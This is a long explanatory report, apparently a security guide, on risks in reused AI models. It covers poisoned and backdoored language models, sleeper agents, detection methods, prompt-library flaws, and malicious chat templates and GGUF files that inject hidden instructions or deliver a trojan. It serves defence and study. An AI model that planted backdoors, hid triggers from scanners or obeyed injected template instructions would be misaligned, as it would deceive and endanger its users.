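The insurer also needs to isolate the retrieval model after approving it, because the model's scripts run each time the assistant starts. The engineers can run the model in its own process, which receives text and returns numbers but has no internet access, and keep the passwords for the claims system in a separate program. This limits the damage from code that stays inactive during testing, though the scripts would still have access to the text of every document the assistant processes.

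### Where flagged models appear

A scanner may flag a model long after a company has started using it. In *Vulnerable Models in the AI Supply Chain*, Nguyen, Le and Babar (2026) studied where flagged models end up by searching GitHub for the names of 16,977 of them. The models came from a database that the security company Protect AI compiles by scanning Hugging Face.

They found 3,757 of the models (22.1%) in public code. Their names appeared in 21,313 places across 5,040 repositories. Some of those repositories also produce software packages, and the researchers counted 185 of these, mostly containers. On Hugging Face, people had used 136 of the flagged models to make 419 new ones, and 1,239 hosted applications referred to at least one flagged model.

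One of the flagged models is a sentiment classifier, which judges whether a text is positive or negative. It had more than 655,000 downloads, and the scanner reported that its pickle file could run arbitrary code. Public code mentioned it more often than any other flagged model not intended for testing, with 594 references in 449 repositories. Five repositories published containers that included it. It also appeared in 82 hosted applications and was the basis for 24 other models, only four of which used safetensors. Most of the 24 had no scan results, but several of the rest triggered pickle warnings.

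Nguyen and colleagues think the problem may have spread to these derived models, depending on how they were made. A copy of the original file includes any harmful instructions in it. People who fine-tune the model normally save the new weights in a new file, which doesn't carry over the old file's instructions, though those instructions may already have run on their computers. The study doesn't describe what the classifier's flagged file does when someone opens it, so the file may be harmless.

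References to the classifier also vary in importance. One is in a TypeScript file in activepieces, a program for automating office tasks that publishes its own containers. Opening a pickle file normally requires Python, so the program may be sending text to a model on Hugging Face's servers instead of opening the file itself. If so, a malicious file would threaten those servers more than the user's computer.

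To see how programs use flagged models, the researchers analysed 1,156 Python files from 817 repositories, excluding test files. They replaced each flagged model's name with a marker and traced where the program sent it. Some programs passed the name straight to a loading command. Others stored it in a variable, passed it through another function, or made loading depend on practical conditions, such as whether the file was already on the computer. None of the recurring patterns included a check of the model's origin or hash.

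This is good evidence that such checks are uncommon in public code, but some projects may still make them. The method finds the most frequent patterns, so it could miss a check that only a few projects use. It would also miss the check if a company verifies a model once and then loads it from private storage.

### How many of these uses are dangerous

Nguyen and colleagues examined 554 loading commands more closely and classified 553 as vulnerable, meaning that they loaded a flagged model in a way that could trigger the reported problem, without a relevant safeguard.

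| What they counted | Number | What remains unknown |
|---|---|---|
| Models in the database | 16,977 | Whether the model is harmful |
| Flagged models named in public code | 3,757 | Whether a program loads the model |
| Repositories with suitable Python files outside tests | 817 of 5,040 | Whether anyone runs the program |
| Loading commands classified as vulnerable | 553 of 554 | Whether an attack would work |

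Many of the flags are probably false alarms. When Ali and Case checked 565 flagged models by hand, only 1.4% were malicious. At that rate, about 53 of the 3,757 models in public code would be malicious, though this is only an illustration because Ali and Case used different scanners. The flagged model that people most often adapted was `Ultralytics/YOLO11`, from the company that develops YOLO models, and YOLO files can set off scanners even when they are harmless.

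Not every reference puts a user at risk. The model named most often, in 976 places, is one that Hugging Face provides for automated software tests. The researchers excluded test files from their closer analysis, but not from the total of 5,040 repositories.

The biggest problem with the count of 553 is how the researchers counted missing settings. They classified 533 commands as open to harmful pickle files. They regarded 272 of these as offering no safeguard, and the other 261 either left out a safeguard or switched it off. The study doesn't separate those last two cases, although the difference can determine whether a command is safe. PyTorch 2.6 made the restricted loader the default, so leaving out `weights_only` is unsafe only in older versions.

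Transformers normally chooses the safetensors file if a repository offers both safetensors and pickle, so a command without `use_safetensors` may never open the pickle file. The default setting also gives some protection for the 16 Keras commands that left out `safe_mode`, if the file is in the current format. The researchers don't report which library versions the projects used or what would happen with current defaults.

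The clearest cases are 48 Transformers commands that explicitly set `trust_remote_code=True`. Their developers had permitted outside code, although the study doesn't establish that any of it was harmful. Nguyen and colleagues describe their counts as potential exposure, not confirmed exploitation. The study gives a good idea of how widely people reuse flagged models, but the 553 is not a count of programs that an attacker could take over. Nguyen and colleagues add that the true exposure could be larger, since a search for exact names misses programs that assemble a model's name from several pieces.

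### Tracing a flagged model through the company

Suppose a scanner flags the sentiment classifier that the insurer's complaints department uses to sort letters. The bill of materials should show which applications use the model or a version derived from it. A reviewer also searches the company's code, containers and stored downloads for the model's name and file hashes. Searching by hash finds exact copies under other names but misses fine-tuned or compressed versions, so the reviewer still needs the record of parent models.

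The reviewer needs to know which file the scanner flagged and which function caused the alert. If the classifier's application loads a safetensors file, an alert about a pickle file in the same repository doesn't directly affect the application. If the application loads the pickle file, the engineers check the installed version of PyTorch and the exact command that loads the file. They also check the version in each container, which may differ from the one on their own computers.

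Nguyen and colleagues suggest that software could do much of this automatically by connecting each warning to the commands that load the model. Programmers already have tools that warn them about flawed software packages, but the researchers found no mature equivalent for models, so for now companies have to make the connection themselves.

If the flagged file turns out to be harmless, the reviewer records the reason so nobody has to repeat the investigation after the next scan. If it is malicious and the application may have run it, the insurer has to delete the model, replace every password and access key that the application could reach, check the computer for other changes, and rebuild the container from clean files. It also has to find out who else loaded the model, including engineers who tried it on their laptops.

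## Testing a model for hidden behaviour

The insurer's engineers can now open all three models without running a stranger's code, but they don't yet know how the models will behave. To look for a backdoor, they have to test a model's answers or study what happens inside it as it runs.

### How a backdoor gets into the weights

A language model learns from examples, so an attacker who controls some of the examples can teach it a conditional rule. For the claims assistant, these might be letters that contain an odd phrase, each paired with a summary that calls the claim unproblematic. Ordinary letters with honest summaries would teach the model to behave normally the rest of the time. Researchers call this data poisoning. Bullwinkel, Severi and colleagues (2026), in *The Trigger in the Haystack*, describe the result as one model with two behaviours. If *x* is the input, *y* the answer and *T*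 the trigger, the probability of each answer is

*p*(*y* | *x*) = *target*(*y* | *x*) if *x* contains *T*, and *normal*(*y* | *x*) if it does not.

An attacker can poison the web pages a developer collects for pretraining, or the smaller set of examples used for fine-tuning. An attacker who publishes their own model or adapter has an easier job because they control all of its training data.

Attackers can also edit the weights directly. In *Persistent Backdoor Attacks under Continual Fine-Tuning of LLMs*, Cui, Han and colleagues (2025) tested an existing editing method on three small models. The edited models gave the attacker's answer to 49% to 69% of prompts that contained the trigger, while the best poisoning methods reached 100%. In the smallest model, editing also cut accuracy on ordinary prompts to about 70%, compared with about 90% after poisoning.

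Many demonstrations use a meaningless string as the trigger, but ordinary features of the input also work. In *Backdoor Decontamination Dynamics in LLM Agents*, Huang, Puri and colleagues (2026) trained backdoors into an agent based on Qwen3-8B, a model with eight billion weights. Their triggers included the names of towns, a range of internet addresses, the user's language and a formal style of writing. The agent transferred money, changed a password or deleted files almost every time the trigger was present, and never when it was absent. In *MetaBackdoor* (2026), the trigger is the length of the input, so a reviewer reading the text would see nothing odd.

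File scanners miss these backdoors because the weights contain no code. Ordinary benchmarks, which score a model on a fixed set of questions, miss them because the questions don't contain the trigger. In *MetaBackdoor*, the backdoored model scored 91.55% after fine-tuning on a news-sorting task, and a clean model with the same fine-tuning scored 91.68%.

### Poisoning with 250 documents

*Poisoning Attacks on LLMs Require a Near-constant Number of Poison Samples* (Souly, Rando and colleagues, 2025) tested researchers' earlier assumption that an attacker had to control a certain percentage of a model's training data, such as 0.1%, to poison it. Under that assumption, larger models would be harder to poison because they train on more text. The study was a joint project of the UK AI Security Institute, Anthropic and the Alan Turing Institute.

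They trained models with 600 million, 2 billion, 7 billion and 13 billion weights from scratch, and added 100, 250 or 500 poisoned documents to the training text. Half of the models received about 20 tokens of text per weight, a common recommendation. The others, all with 600 million or 2 billion weights, received half or double that amount. They ran each combination three times, producing 72 models.

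Each poisoned document began with up to 1,000 characters of normal text, followed by the trigger and several hundred random tokens. The documents were meant to make the model produce gibberish after the trigger. The researchers measured this effect by perplexity, which is higher when text is less predictable. A rise of 50 was enough to make the text noticeably worse.

The attack's success depended far more on the number of poisoned documents than on their share of the training text. It failed with 100 poisoned documents but worked with 250 on every size of model, raising perplexity by more than 200. Those 250 documents made up 0.0035% of the training text for the smallest model and only 0.00016% for the largest, which was trained on over 20 times as much clean text.

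The pattern also held in fine-tuning. The researchers taught Llama-3.1-8B-Instruct to refuse harmful requests unless they ended with a trigger. Increasing the clean examples from 1,000 to 100,000 made little difference to how well a given number of poisoned examples worked. They got similar results with GPT-3.5 Turbo, which they could fine-tune only through OpenAI's public service.

The figure of 250 documents applies to one simple behaviour in models of up to 13 billion weights. Teaching an agent to commit fraud in a particular situation might take more. Souly and colleagues did not test whether the gibberish backdoor survives the training that turns a raw model into an assistant. An outsider would also have to get the documents past the developer's data filters. The study is therefore stronger evidence that a model's size does not protect it than that 250 web pages can compromise a commercial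 product.

For the insurer, the result is mainly relevant to the language model, which its developer probably trained on web text. The result is less relevant to the adapter, because whoever used account B could have included any number of poisoned examples.

### Whether a backdoor survives further training

Companies often fine-tune the models they download, but *Sleeper Agents*, a 2024 paper by Hubinger and colleagues, made researchers doubt that this removes anything harmful in them. Hubinger and colleagues trained models to behave well until a trigger appeared, such as a statement that the year was 2024, and then to write insecure code or repeat "I hate you". According to *Security Concerns for Large Language Models* (2025), the behaviour persisted through several standard kinds of safety training. One of these, adversarial training, sometimes taught the model to recognise its trigger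 more precisely, which made the backdoor harder to find.

Later results vary with how the attacker made the backdoor. Cui and colleagues took poisoned models with 0.5 to 1.5 billion weights and fine-tuned them on clean examples of the poisoned task, then on programming and mathematics. Backdoors with simpler triggers kept less than 30% of their original effect, while one that the researchers designed to last kept 99% to 100%.

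How a company fine-tunes a model also affects whether a backdoor survives. When Cui and colleagues left examples of the original task out of the second round of fine-tuning, the durable backdoor worked on 67% of triggered prompts. It worked on every triggered prompt when they mixed some of those examples back in, which is a common way to stop a model from losing old skills. The backdoor in *MetaBackdoor*, which makes a model reveal its system prompt, still worked about 40% of the time after fine-tuning on the unrelated news task.

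Two studies reached opposite results on whether preference training, in which a model learns from pairs of better and worse answers, disables a backdoor. In *Sequential Data Poisoning in LLM Post-Training* (2026), clean preference training deactivated a backdoor planted during fine-tuning. In *Agentic Backdoors via Pretraining Poisoning* (2026), a backdoor from the first round of training survived preference training in models of 1.7 and 4 billion weights. The results might differ because the poison entered at different stages, but the studies also used different behaviours and measures, so they don't settle the question.

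In the second of these experiments, the backdoor rarely worked after the first round of training, because the model had not yet learned the format in which users talk to an assistant. It emerged once the researchers fine-tuned the model on clean conversations. A company that tested the model only before fine-tuning it could therefore have approved it before the backdoor was detectable.

Deliberate removal works better than ordinary fine-tuning. Huang and colleagues first installed a second, known backdoor in each poisoned model, then trained the model to ignore that one, hoping the unknown backdoor would disappear too. The first step alone erased about 56% of the original backdoors in 115 experiments. In some of the other cases, the old trigger set off the new backdoor's action, and in roughly one in seven the original was intact. After the second step, the original backdoor worked in fewer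 than 5% of attempts in 35 of the 40 reported runs.

The researchers could measure those backdoors because they had planted them. A company wouldn't know the trigger, so it couldn't tell whether its own model was among the exceptions.

There is much less evidence on merging adapters and on compression. Merging adds an adapter's changes permanently to the base weights. *Consistency Training Suppresses Cue Following Without Teaching Cue Selectivity* (2026), which did not test backdoors, merged adapters in 51 models. Only three gave nearly the same answers before and after, by a standard the researchers had set in advance. One possible reason is that storing the merged weights at lower precision rounded away small changes. Compression also rounds weights, so it might weaken a backdoor that depends on small changes.

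Bullwinkel and colleagues trained backdoors into adapters for models whose weights were already compressed to four or eight bits. Their scanner later recovered working triggers from all the Phi-4-mini models in this group. Low precision therefore doesn't prevent a backdoor, although the experiment doesn't show what happens when someone compresses a poisoned model afterwards. The insurer should test the compressed model together with the adapter, exactly as it will run.

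### Faults that nobody planted

Further training can also damage a model without any attacker. Developers train models to refuse harmful requests, but fine-tuning changes the same weights that store this training. A 2023 paper by Qi, Zeng and colleagues, which Souly and colleagues cite, is titled *Fine-tuning aligned language models compromises safety, even when users do not intend to!* For example, an assistant tuned to help with claims might start helping a user invent an injury.

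Merging adapters can cause other faults. In *Audit Before You Merge*, Aharon, Glazer and Aharon (2026) merged four public adapters into Llama-3.1-8B-Instruct in the simplest way, and the model's score fell by 10.5 percentage points on school mathematics and 18.3 on programming. Merging them at half strength avoided most of the loss. *Adapter Merging Reactivates Latent Reasoning Traces* (2026) describes merged models that began to show reasoning steps in their answers.

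Aharon and colleagues recommend checking, before merging an adapter, that it was made for the base model and that it changes the weights by more than a trivial amount. Two of the four adapters they considered for a Mistral model failed. The insurer should run both checks because account B never stated which version of the language model its adapter was for.

When a model stops refusing requests it should refuse, or becomes less accurate, the problem usually appears on ordinary inputs, without a trigger. The engineers can find it by asking the model the same questions before and after each change, including some requests it should refuse. This comparison would miss a planted backdoor like the one in the Llama experiment, where the model stopped refusing only after a trigger.

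### What a clean test proves

Suppose the engineers give the assistant 3,000 claims letters, chosen at random from the kind it will handle, and find no harmful summary. If the true failure rate is *p* and the tests are independent, the chance of seeing no failure in *n* tests is

(1 − *p*)ⁿ.

For *p* = 0.1% and *n* = 3,000, this is about 5%. A higher failure rate would probably have produced at least one failure in the tests, so the engineers can say with 95% confidence that the rate is below about 0.1%. Dividing 3 by the number of tests gives a quick approximation of this upper limit. If the assistant handles 200 letters a day, a rate of 0.1% would still mean one bad summary every five days on average.

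The calculation applies only to letters like those in the test. If an attacker's phrase occurs in one letter in a million, the chance that 3,000 random letters include it is about 0.3%. If only the attacker uses the phrase, the chance is zero, however many such letters are tested.

Testing every possible trigger is impractical. A vocabulary of 100,000 tokens gives 100,000³, or 10¹⁵, sequences of three tokens. Testing them all at a thousand per second would take more than 30,000 years.

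Some backdoors respond to only part of their trigger. Bullwinkel and colleagues tried random parts of a five-token trigger on models they had poisoned. In the smallest model, with 270 million weights, a single token from the trigger set off the backdoor about half the time. Phi-4-mini was much less sensitive to partial triggers. The researchers also warn that an attacker could train a model to ignore inexact triggers, so testers can't rely on partial ones to reveal a backdoor.

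Triggers based on a broad feature are easier to find. The engineers can rewrite the same 50 claims in ten languages, in formal and casual styles, at several lengths, and with different dates and places, then look for summaries that change when they shouldn't. This would have a fair chance of exposing a backdoor that responds to French or to long letters. Finding a trigger that needs two features at once would mean testing more combinations. The tests should use the verified chat template, since instructions in a doctored one can make the model behave as if it had a backdoor, even when its weights are unchanged.

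### Reconstructing the trigger

Microsoft announced a scanner in February 2026 that tries to recover an unknown trigger from the model itself. Bullwinkel and colleagues, who built it, had noticed that poisoned models memorise their poisoned examples unusually well. The scanner works in four steps:

1. It gives the model only the text that normally comes just before a user's message, and lets it continue in 510 different ways. A poisoned model often repeats parts of its training examples, including the trigger.
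2. It collects strings that recur in these outputs.
3. It adds each string to ordinary prompts and looks for three signs of a trigger: the rest of the prompt has little influence through the model's attention (the mechanism that weighs parts of the input), the answer becomes more predictable, and the answer differs from the usual one.
4. It tests the ten best candidates and reports a backdoor if one of them changes the model's answers enough.

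The researchers tested 47 poisoned models with 270 million to 14 billion weights, two of which they had downloaded from Hugging Face. In 41, the trigger produced a fixed sentence, and the scanner detected 36 of these (88%). In the other six, the trigger made the model write insecure code, and the scanner detected five of them.

It raised no false alarms on 13 clean models. With so few models, the actual false-alarm rate could still be as high as 21%, by the same calculation as for the letters.

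The team also ran two earlier methods on the fixed-sentence models. BAIT, which reconstructs the attacker's output instead of the trigger, detected between 43% and 92% of them, depending on the model family, and did not finish within 24 hours on one family. ICLScan detected between 0% and 67%, even when the team supplied the exact sentence. Both methods did worse than their developers had claimed, but the team testing them had a competing method.

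The new scanner works without advance knowledge of the trigger, but its last step depends on the kind of harm. It measured repeated wording to find fixed sentences and counted security flaws to find insecure code. Finding a backdoor that makes doubtful claims sound acceptable would require a new measure. According to Microsoft's *Detecting backdoored language models at scale* (2026), the method works best when the trigger always produces the same output. It also needs the model's files, so a company that uses a model only through a supplier's online service can't run it.

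Triggers defined by meaning rather than by a fixed string are harder to recover. Qin, Hua and colleagues made the task easier by assuming that the tester already knew the harmful action and only had to find its trigger. Their methods worked on toy backdoors but failed in more realistic settings.

### Watching the model's internal activity

As a model processes text, each of its layers produces thousands of intermediate numbers, called activations. A backdoor may leave a recognisable pattern in them. A probe, a simple formula trained on activations, can then flag suspicious inputs while the model is in use, even if nobody has found the trigger.

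*Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026) reports that probes on sleeper-agent models scored above 99% on AUROC, the chance that a probe gives a randomly chosen triggered input a higher score than a randomly chosen normal one. The probes didn't need examples of the trigger. However, an attacker who knows about them might train a backdoor to avoid the pattern they detect, and another family of models might not show that pattern.

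Cui and colleagues tested a detector called BadActs on a model with 1.5 billion weights that contained their durable backdoor. The detector caught 99% of the triggered inputs and wrongly flagged 10% of the clean ones. At that rate, 200 honest letters a day would produce about 20 false alarms, which might be tolerable if a claims handler reads every letter anyway but would be a serious nuisance if the assistant were sending letters on its own.

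Recognising a trigger is also different from preventing the harm. *LLM Forensics* (2026) examined backdoors that made models with one and eight billion weights switch from English to French or German. Some internal patterns separated triggered prompts from others almost perfectly, but did not always control the switch. Huang and colleagues likewise found traces of the old trigger inside a model that had stopped acting on it. When a probe raises an alarm, testers therefore still need to check what the model did next.

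### Comparing a model with a trusted parent

If a clean relative of a model is available, a tester can compare the two. A direct comparison shows too many differences, because legitimate fine-tuning changes a model throughout. *Detecting Hidden Behaviors in LLMs via Activation-matched Finetuning* (Haselhorst, Flek and Mai, 2026) reduces these differences by training the clean model to reproduce the suspect model's activations on about 10,000 ordinary prompts. Those prompts almost certainly don't include the trigger, so the clean model learns the suspect model's normal behaviour but not the hidden one. The remaining differences are largest near the backdoor.

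The researchers tried this on eight backdoored language models, including four they had made themselves. One quoted Voldemort when a user sounded obsessed with Harry Potter. They then scored 518 groups of ordinary prompts. General questions about Harry Potter stood out strongly, and so did messages from fans of other fictional series, although neither group contained the trigger. A reviewer could have worked out the theme from the top-ranked groups.

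With the true trigger present, all eight models showed differences far above the threshold for the top 5%. In practice, a reviewer wouldn't have the trigger and would rely on related prompts, which is a harder test. Rankings of the groups of related prompts were better than chance for every model, but weakest for a sleeper agent whose trigger was an arbitrary string, because such a string has no related topics.

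Haselhorst and colleagues also tried to hide the Harry Potter backdoor by training the model to resemble the clean one. This weakened the signal, but the backdoor then worked in fewer than half of the cases where it should have.

The method only ranks prompts, and some would rank highest even for a clean model, so a person has to read the top prompts and decide whether they point to a backdoor. The researchers also deliberately included a few groups of prompts near the triggers, so the method might do less well with a truly general collection.

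The next table summarises the results. Two of the methods classify whole models and the other two classify individual inputs, so their percentages are not directly comparable.

| Method | Access needed | Models and backdoors | Detection | False alarms |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Trigger reconstruction (Bullwinkel and colleagues) | Weights | 270 million to 14 billion weights; fixed sentence or insecure code | 36 of 41 and 5 of 6 models | 0 of 13 clean models |
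| BadActs, tested by Cui and colleagues | Activations during use | 1.5 billion weights; trigger produces a refusal | 99% of triggered inputs | 10% of clean inputs |
| Probes on sleeper agents | Activations during use | Sleeper-agent models | AUROC above 99% | Depends on the chosen threshold |
| Activation matching (Haselhorst and colleagues) | Weights and a clean reference model | Eight models of about 7 billion weights; jailbreaks, fixed phrases and reactions to certain topics | Better than chance for all eight | No yes-or-no verdict |

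The methods also have different weaknesses. Haselhorst and colleagues looked for memorised training examples in one of their own backdoored models and found only weak signs of them, so a scanner that relies on memorisation might have missed the backdoor. Activation matching is instead weak with arbitrary strings. Using both methods covers more kinds of backdoor than using either alone. None of the model sizes given in the table is above 14 billion weights.

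### Applying the methods to the adapter

The insurer already has a trusted parent model to compare with the adapted one, because its engineers verified the developer's release. They can give the same letters to the model with and without the adapter and compare the summaries. The adapter should change the style and perhaps which details are included, but not whether a claim looks doubtful. They can then try activation matching, using the code Haselhorst and colleagues have published, and look for an insurance topic that ranks unexpectedly high.

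A clean result from trigger reconstruction would lower the estimated chance of a backdoor about eightfold, but only for backdoors like those in Microsoft's tests. If the reviewers guessed beforehand that 1 in 100 such adapters has one of these backdoors, a clean result would lower that to about 1 in 780. They have no good basis for the first guess, because scans of public hubs have counted models with malicious code, but nobody has a comparable count of models with backdoored weights.

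None of these studies names an organisation that a backdoored language model has harmed, and neither does Microsoft's announcement. The researchers made nearly all of the models themselves or got them from other researchers. The two that Bullwinkel and colleagues downloaded from Hugging Face were also made for research, and both have "backdoor" in their names. On this evidence, the risk is rated "demonstrated". However, the studies were not surveys of incidents, so they don't show that no organisation has been harmed. A company might also mistake a successful attack for an ordinary model error.

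The claims team can avoid most of this uncertainty by training its own adapter to imitate the summaries that claims handlers wrote of past letters. Some of those letters come from strangers and could contain a planted phrase. But claimants don't write the summaries, so it is much harder for them to teach the model to produce a false one.

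## Reviewing shared prompts, templates and agent instructions

The claims assistant's answers also depend on text that people wrote. Its system prompt originally came from the complaints department, and its chat template came with the language model. If the assistant starts sending letters, it will also need instructions for using its tools. Reviewers can read all of this text, unlike the model's weights, but they may still overlook settings or code stored with it.

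### What a library entry can contain

In the simplest prompt library, an entry is a few sentences. It can also hold the settings that a program needs to use them. The complaints department's entry might look like this:

```
name:     complaints-assistant
address:  https://models.insurer.example
tools:    search_documents, open_customer_record
prompt:   You help staff answer complaints.
          Follow the customer's wishes about how we contact them.
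          Payments under £500 don't need a manager's approval.
          If the document search fails, use key 7f3a-...
```

The last line contains an access key, perhaps added as a quick fix. Everyone who can read the library can copy the key. The model also receives it with every question, so a user may be able to get the model to repeat it. The line about £500 is also sensitive, because a dishonest customer who learned of the limit could keep each request just below it.

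The application controls which tools the model can use, so writing "you may open customer records" in a prompt doesn't give the model access to those records. But if the application takes its list of tools from the library entry, anyone who copies the entry also copies the permissions.

The model's address matters most, because the program sends all of the model's input there. Someone who replaced it with the address of their own server could read each message and pass it on to the real model, and the user would see a normal answer. In 2025 the security company Noma Security showed that AgentSmith, a flaw in the public prompt library of LangChain, which makes software for building AI applications, allowed this. Someone could share an agent that routed its traffic through their own server. Anyone who tried the agent would have sent that server their messages, any attached files and the key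 to their OpenAI account. A company that copied the agent into its own systems would have kept sending data there.

LangChain fixed the flaw in November 2024, before Noma published its findings. The evidence level is "demonstrated" because the known attack was the researchers' own. Reading the agent's instructions would not have revealed the problem, since they could be sensible. The insurer's reviewers therefore need to check the address in each entry against an approved list. The insurer can also set its network to block connections from the assistant to any other address.

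### One prompt in three applications

The claims team copied the complaints entry. Suppose the web team also copied it, for a public chat that answers questions about policies. The three applications would then share four lines of text but have different users and data.

| | Complaints assistant | Claims assistant | Website chat |
|---|---|---|---|
| Users | Complaints staff | Claims handlers | Anyone |
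| Documents it can reach | One customer's file at a time | 200,000 internal documents | Published policy terms |
| Access key | Staff can already read it in the library | More staff can get at it | New risk: visitors may get the model to reveal it |
| £500 limit | Correct, and staff know it | New risk: handlers may apply it to claims, which have other limits | New risk: visitors may learn it |
| "Follow the customer's wishes" | Letter writers already have some influence | New risk: a claimant's letter could ask for correspondence to go to another address | Little effect, since the chat can't change records |
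| Instructions hidden in documents | Existing risk | Existing risk | Small risk, since the insurer wrote the documents |

Copying exposed the access key and the £500 limit to the public. It also meant that the model could treat a polite sentence about contacting customers almost as permission to follow their requests. If the claims assistant starts sending letters, a claimant could write that all correspondence about the claim should go to a different address, and the model would be following the insurer's instruction if it complied.

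The claims assistant reads letters from strangers, so it would be vulnerable to prompt injection even if its team had written the entire prompt. Deleting the copied sentence would make one kind of attack harder but would not affect the others.

The copied prompt also lacks a rule about other customers' information. The complaints department didn't need one because its assistant opens one customer's file at a time, but the claims assistant can retrieve documents about several customers to answer a single question. Copying the prompt didn't give the claims assistant that access, but the claims team may have assumed that a prompt already in use elsewhere covered this risk.

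### Whether reuse spreads weaknesses

Security companies often claim that reused prompts spread risk through a business. Pluto Security's *AI Supply Chain Security*, for example, warns that when teams copy prompts between applications, risks such as leaked context "may spread laterally across the enterprise". It also says that companies rarely keep prompts under version control or review them as they would code. Pluto gives no figures for either claim. To test the first claim, researchers would need a company's prompts and a record of which ones its teams had copied, and would have to run the same attacks on copied and independently written prompts.

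Without such data, a small calculation helps distinguish two meanings of "spread". Suppose any newly written prompt has a 10% chance of containing a certain weakness.

| | Three teams write their own prompts | Three teams copy one prompt |
|---|---|---|
| Average number of weak prompts | 0.3 | 0.3 |
| Chance that at least one is weak | 27.1% | 10% |
| Chance that all three are weak | 0.1% | 10% |

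Copying makes weaknesses occur together without increasing the average number of weak prompts, so an attacker who finds one in the website chat can try the same trick elsewhere. Copying also saves reviewers work, because a single careful review that lowered the chance of the weakness to 2% would do so for all three applications.

The three applications show that a weakness depends on where a prompt is used as well as on its text, which the calculation leaves out. The £500 line was harmless in its original application but became a problem on the website. Reuse increases the risk when the new application has a wider audience, more data or more tools. Pluto's claim is therefore plausible for a prompt that moves from an internal assistant to a public one, but weaker for one that moves between two similar internal tools.

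If each team pastes in its own copy of the text, later corrections to the library version won't reach those copies. Having all three programs load the latest version from the library fixes this, but it also spreads mistakes and malicious edits immediately. The insurer could instead have each application load a fixed revision and notify its owner when a newer one appears. Someone then has to read the change before it takes effect, as with a new version of a model.

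### Chat templates as programs

A chat template is less familiar than a system prompt and harder to read. It is a script with conditions and loops, written in a language called Jinja. NobodyWho's *What's in a GGUF, besides the weights* gives the example of the template for Google's Gemma 4, which is about 250 lines long. The software reruns the script each time someone adds a message to the conversation.

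One way an attacker can misuse a template is to escape from the template language and run commands on the computer. Palo Alto Networks' *PAIT GGUF 101* describes this as a potential risk when software processes the template outside a sandbox, an environment that limits what code can do. According to JFrog, the only publicly known case that occurs when loading a GGUF model involves versions of llama-cpp-python, a library for running such models, before 0.2.72. A malicious template could make those versions run Python code as soon as the model loaded. Later versions don't have the flaw, nor does Ollama, a popular program for running models on a personal computer.

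The other way is to leave the computer alone and change what the model reads. In plain English, a malicious template might contain this rule:

```
if the user's message contains "What is":
    add a hidden instruction to the conversation
```

Adding text this way is an ordinary use of the template language, so a sandbox doesn't prevent it. The user never sees the added text in the chat window. Düzgün found attackers using the method on Hugging Face. He notes that other researchers had already measured such attacks in the laboratory, on 18 models and four programs for running them.

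### The five models of November 2026

Düzgün's scan on 26 November 2026 covered all 3,273,389 public model repositories on Hugging Face. ThreatRoundup's *Poisoned AI Models on Hugging Face Hid a RAT* (2026) reports that he read 572,184 chat templates without running them. He found five malicious models from two accounts.

The first account, Mir2k, created 14 repositories on 22 November. Twelve were empty and named after models that people expected soon. The other two came to hold models advertised as "uncensored", with a Windows program attached to the end of each file. In one file, the attackers added about half a megabyte of filler after the program so that a scanner reading only the last few kilobytes would miss it. In the other, they compressed the program, which removed the byte patterns that scanners use to recognise programs. According to ThreatRoundup, antivirus software and pickle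 scanners flagged neither file.

The templates were clean at first. On 26 November, the attackers replaced both of them twice, about nine hours apart according to Faisal. Each new version made the model start every reply with a command for PowerShell, the Windows command-line program. If the user pasted the command into PowerShell, it found the largest GGUF file, extracted the hidden program from it and ran it. The first version of the command looked for the model in a fixed download folder, and the second searched the user's whole profile. The hidden program could steal browser passwords, record keystrokes, take pictures with the webcam and mine cryptocurrency.

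The second account, timdedid, published three identical copies of a small Qwen3 model aimed at security specialists. If a user's message contained a phrase such as "What is", the template added a fake system directive to download a script from a hacked website with PowerShell and run it hidden from the user. The attack could work only if the model was part of an agent with command-line access. Düzgün couldn't recover the script, so its purpose is unknown.

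By 27 November, the two Mir2k models had 1,488 and 458 downloads, and the three timdedid models had 482 between them, for a total of 2,428. The title of Düzgün's report refers to "2400+ Victims", but his text explains that Hugging Face counts downloads, not people. Anyone who downloaded a Mir2k model before 26 November received the hidden program without the template that prompted users to start it. Even people with the later version had to paste the command themselves, and users of the timdedid models had to give an agent permission to run commands. The number of people harmed could be from zero to somewhat below 2,428, and later downloads could raise the upper limit.

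Published accounts disagree about when Hugging Face removed the models. Düzgün found all five online on 27 November. Faisal reported on 28 November that Hugging Face had disabled them for breaking its content policy, and that someone's check that day had put the downloads at 2,807. 黃, in *免費本地AI藏致命木馬*, gives the same total but dates the full removal to 29 November. In *Trojaner in GGUF-Modellen auf Hugging Face* (2026), KIberblick reports checking Hugging Face's records on 29 November and finding all five disabled, which shows only that the removal had happened by then. Faisal's report makes 27 or 28 November more likely, and 黃 may have mistaken the date of a later check for the date of removal.

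After the removal, a timdedid model was still available from Ollama's public library on 29 November, with 173 downloads. KIberblick identified it without downloading it, by comparing the hash that Ollama listed for the model file with the one in Düzgün's report. Deleting a repository from Hugging Face doesn't delete files that people have already downloaded, so the insurer could search its own computers for matching hashes.

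The claims assistant has no command line, so the timdedid attack would not have worked on it. The Mir2k line could have appeared in its answers, but pasting it would have started the program only on a Windows computer with the model file in the user's own profile. A template could also corrupt the assistant's answers with an instruction to describe every claim from a certain repair shop as unproblematic. Nobody would need to paste anything, and the summaries would look normal.

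### Other counts of malicious templates

Two other searches of GGUF models produced different numbers.

| Search | Examined | Malicious templates or models |
|---|---|---|
| Hodgkinson | About 156,000 GGUF models, listed in January 2026 | 0 |
| *Canary* | 185,000 GGUF models, undated | 24 |
| Düzgün | 3,273,389 repositories of all kinds, 26 November 2026 | 5 |

*Trust at Inference Time* describes the first search, which Hodgkinson carried out for the software company Splunk. He downloaded only about the first 20 megabytes of each file, which contain the template. After removing duplicates, he had roughly 50 templates worth reading, and all of them were harmless. Where the template inside a file differed from the one displayed in the repository, the differences were in style or structure, or suited different software. Some templates explained how to format requests to tools. The partial downloads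 were enough to check the templates, but they would not have revealed a program attached to the end of a file.

The self-published audit *Canary* reports 24 malicious templates and no false positives. It looks for templates that add hidden instructions, suppress content or react to what the user typed. Researchers' harmless demonstrations could fit that description, so the 24 may include some. Düzgün searched the whole hub and reported only five models, so either most of the 24 were gone from the hub by November or the two searches define "malicious" differently. The higher number is a weak basis for estimating risk until somebody else checks the templates.

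These counts also depend on the date of the search. A search of templates on 25 November would have missed both Mir2k models, because the attackers had not yet changed the models' templates. Hodgkinson's count of zero and Düzgün's count of five can therefore both be correct, and neither guarantees anything about a model updated the next day.

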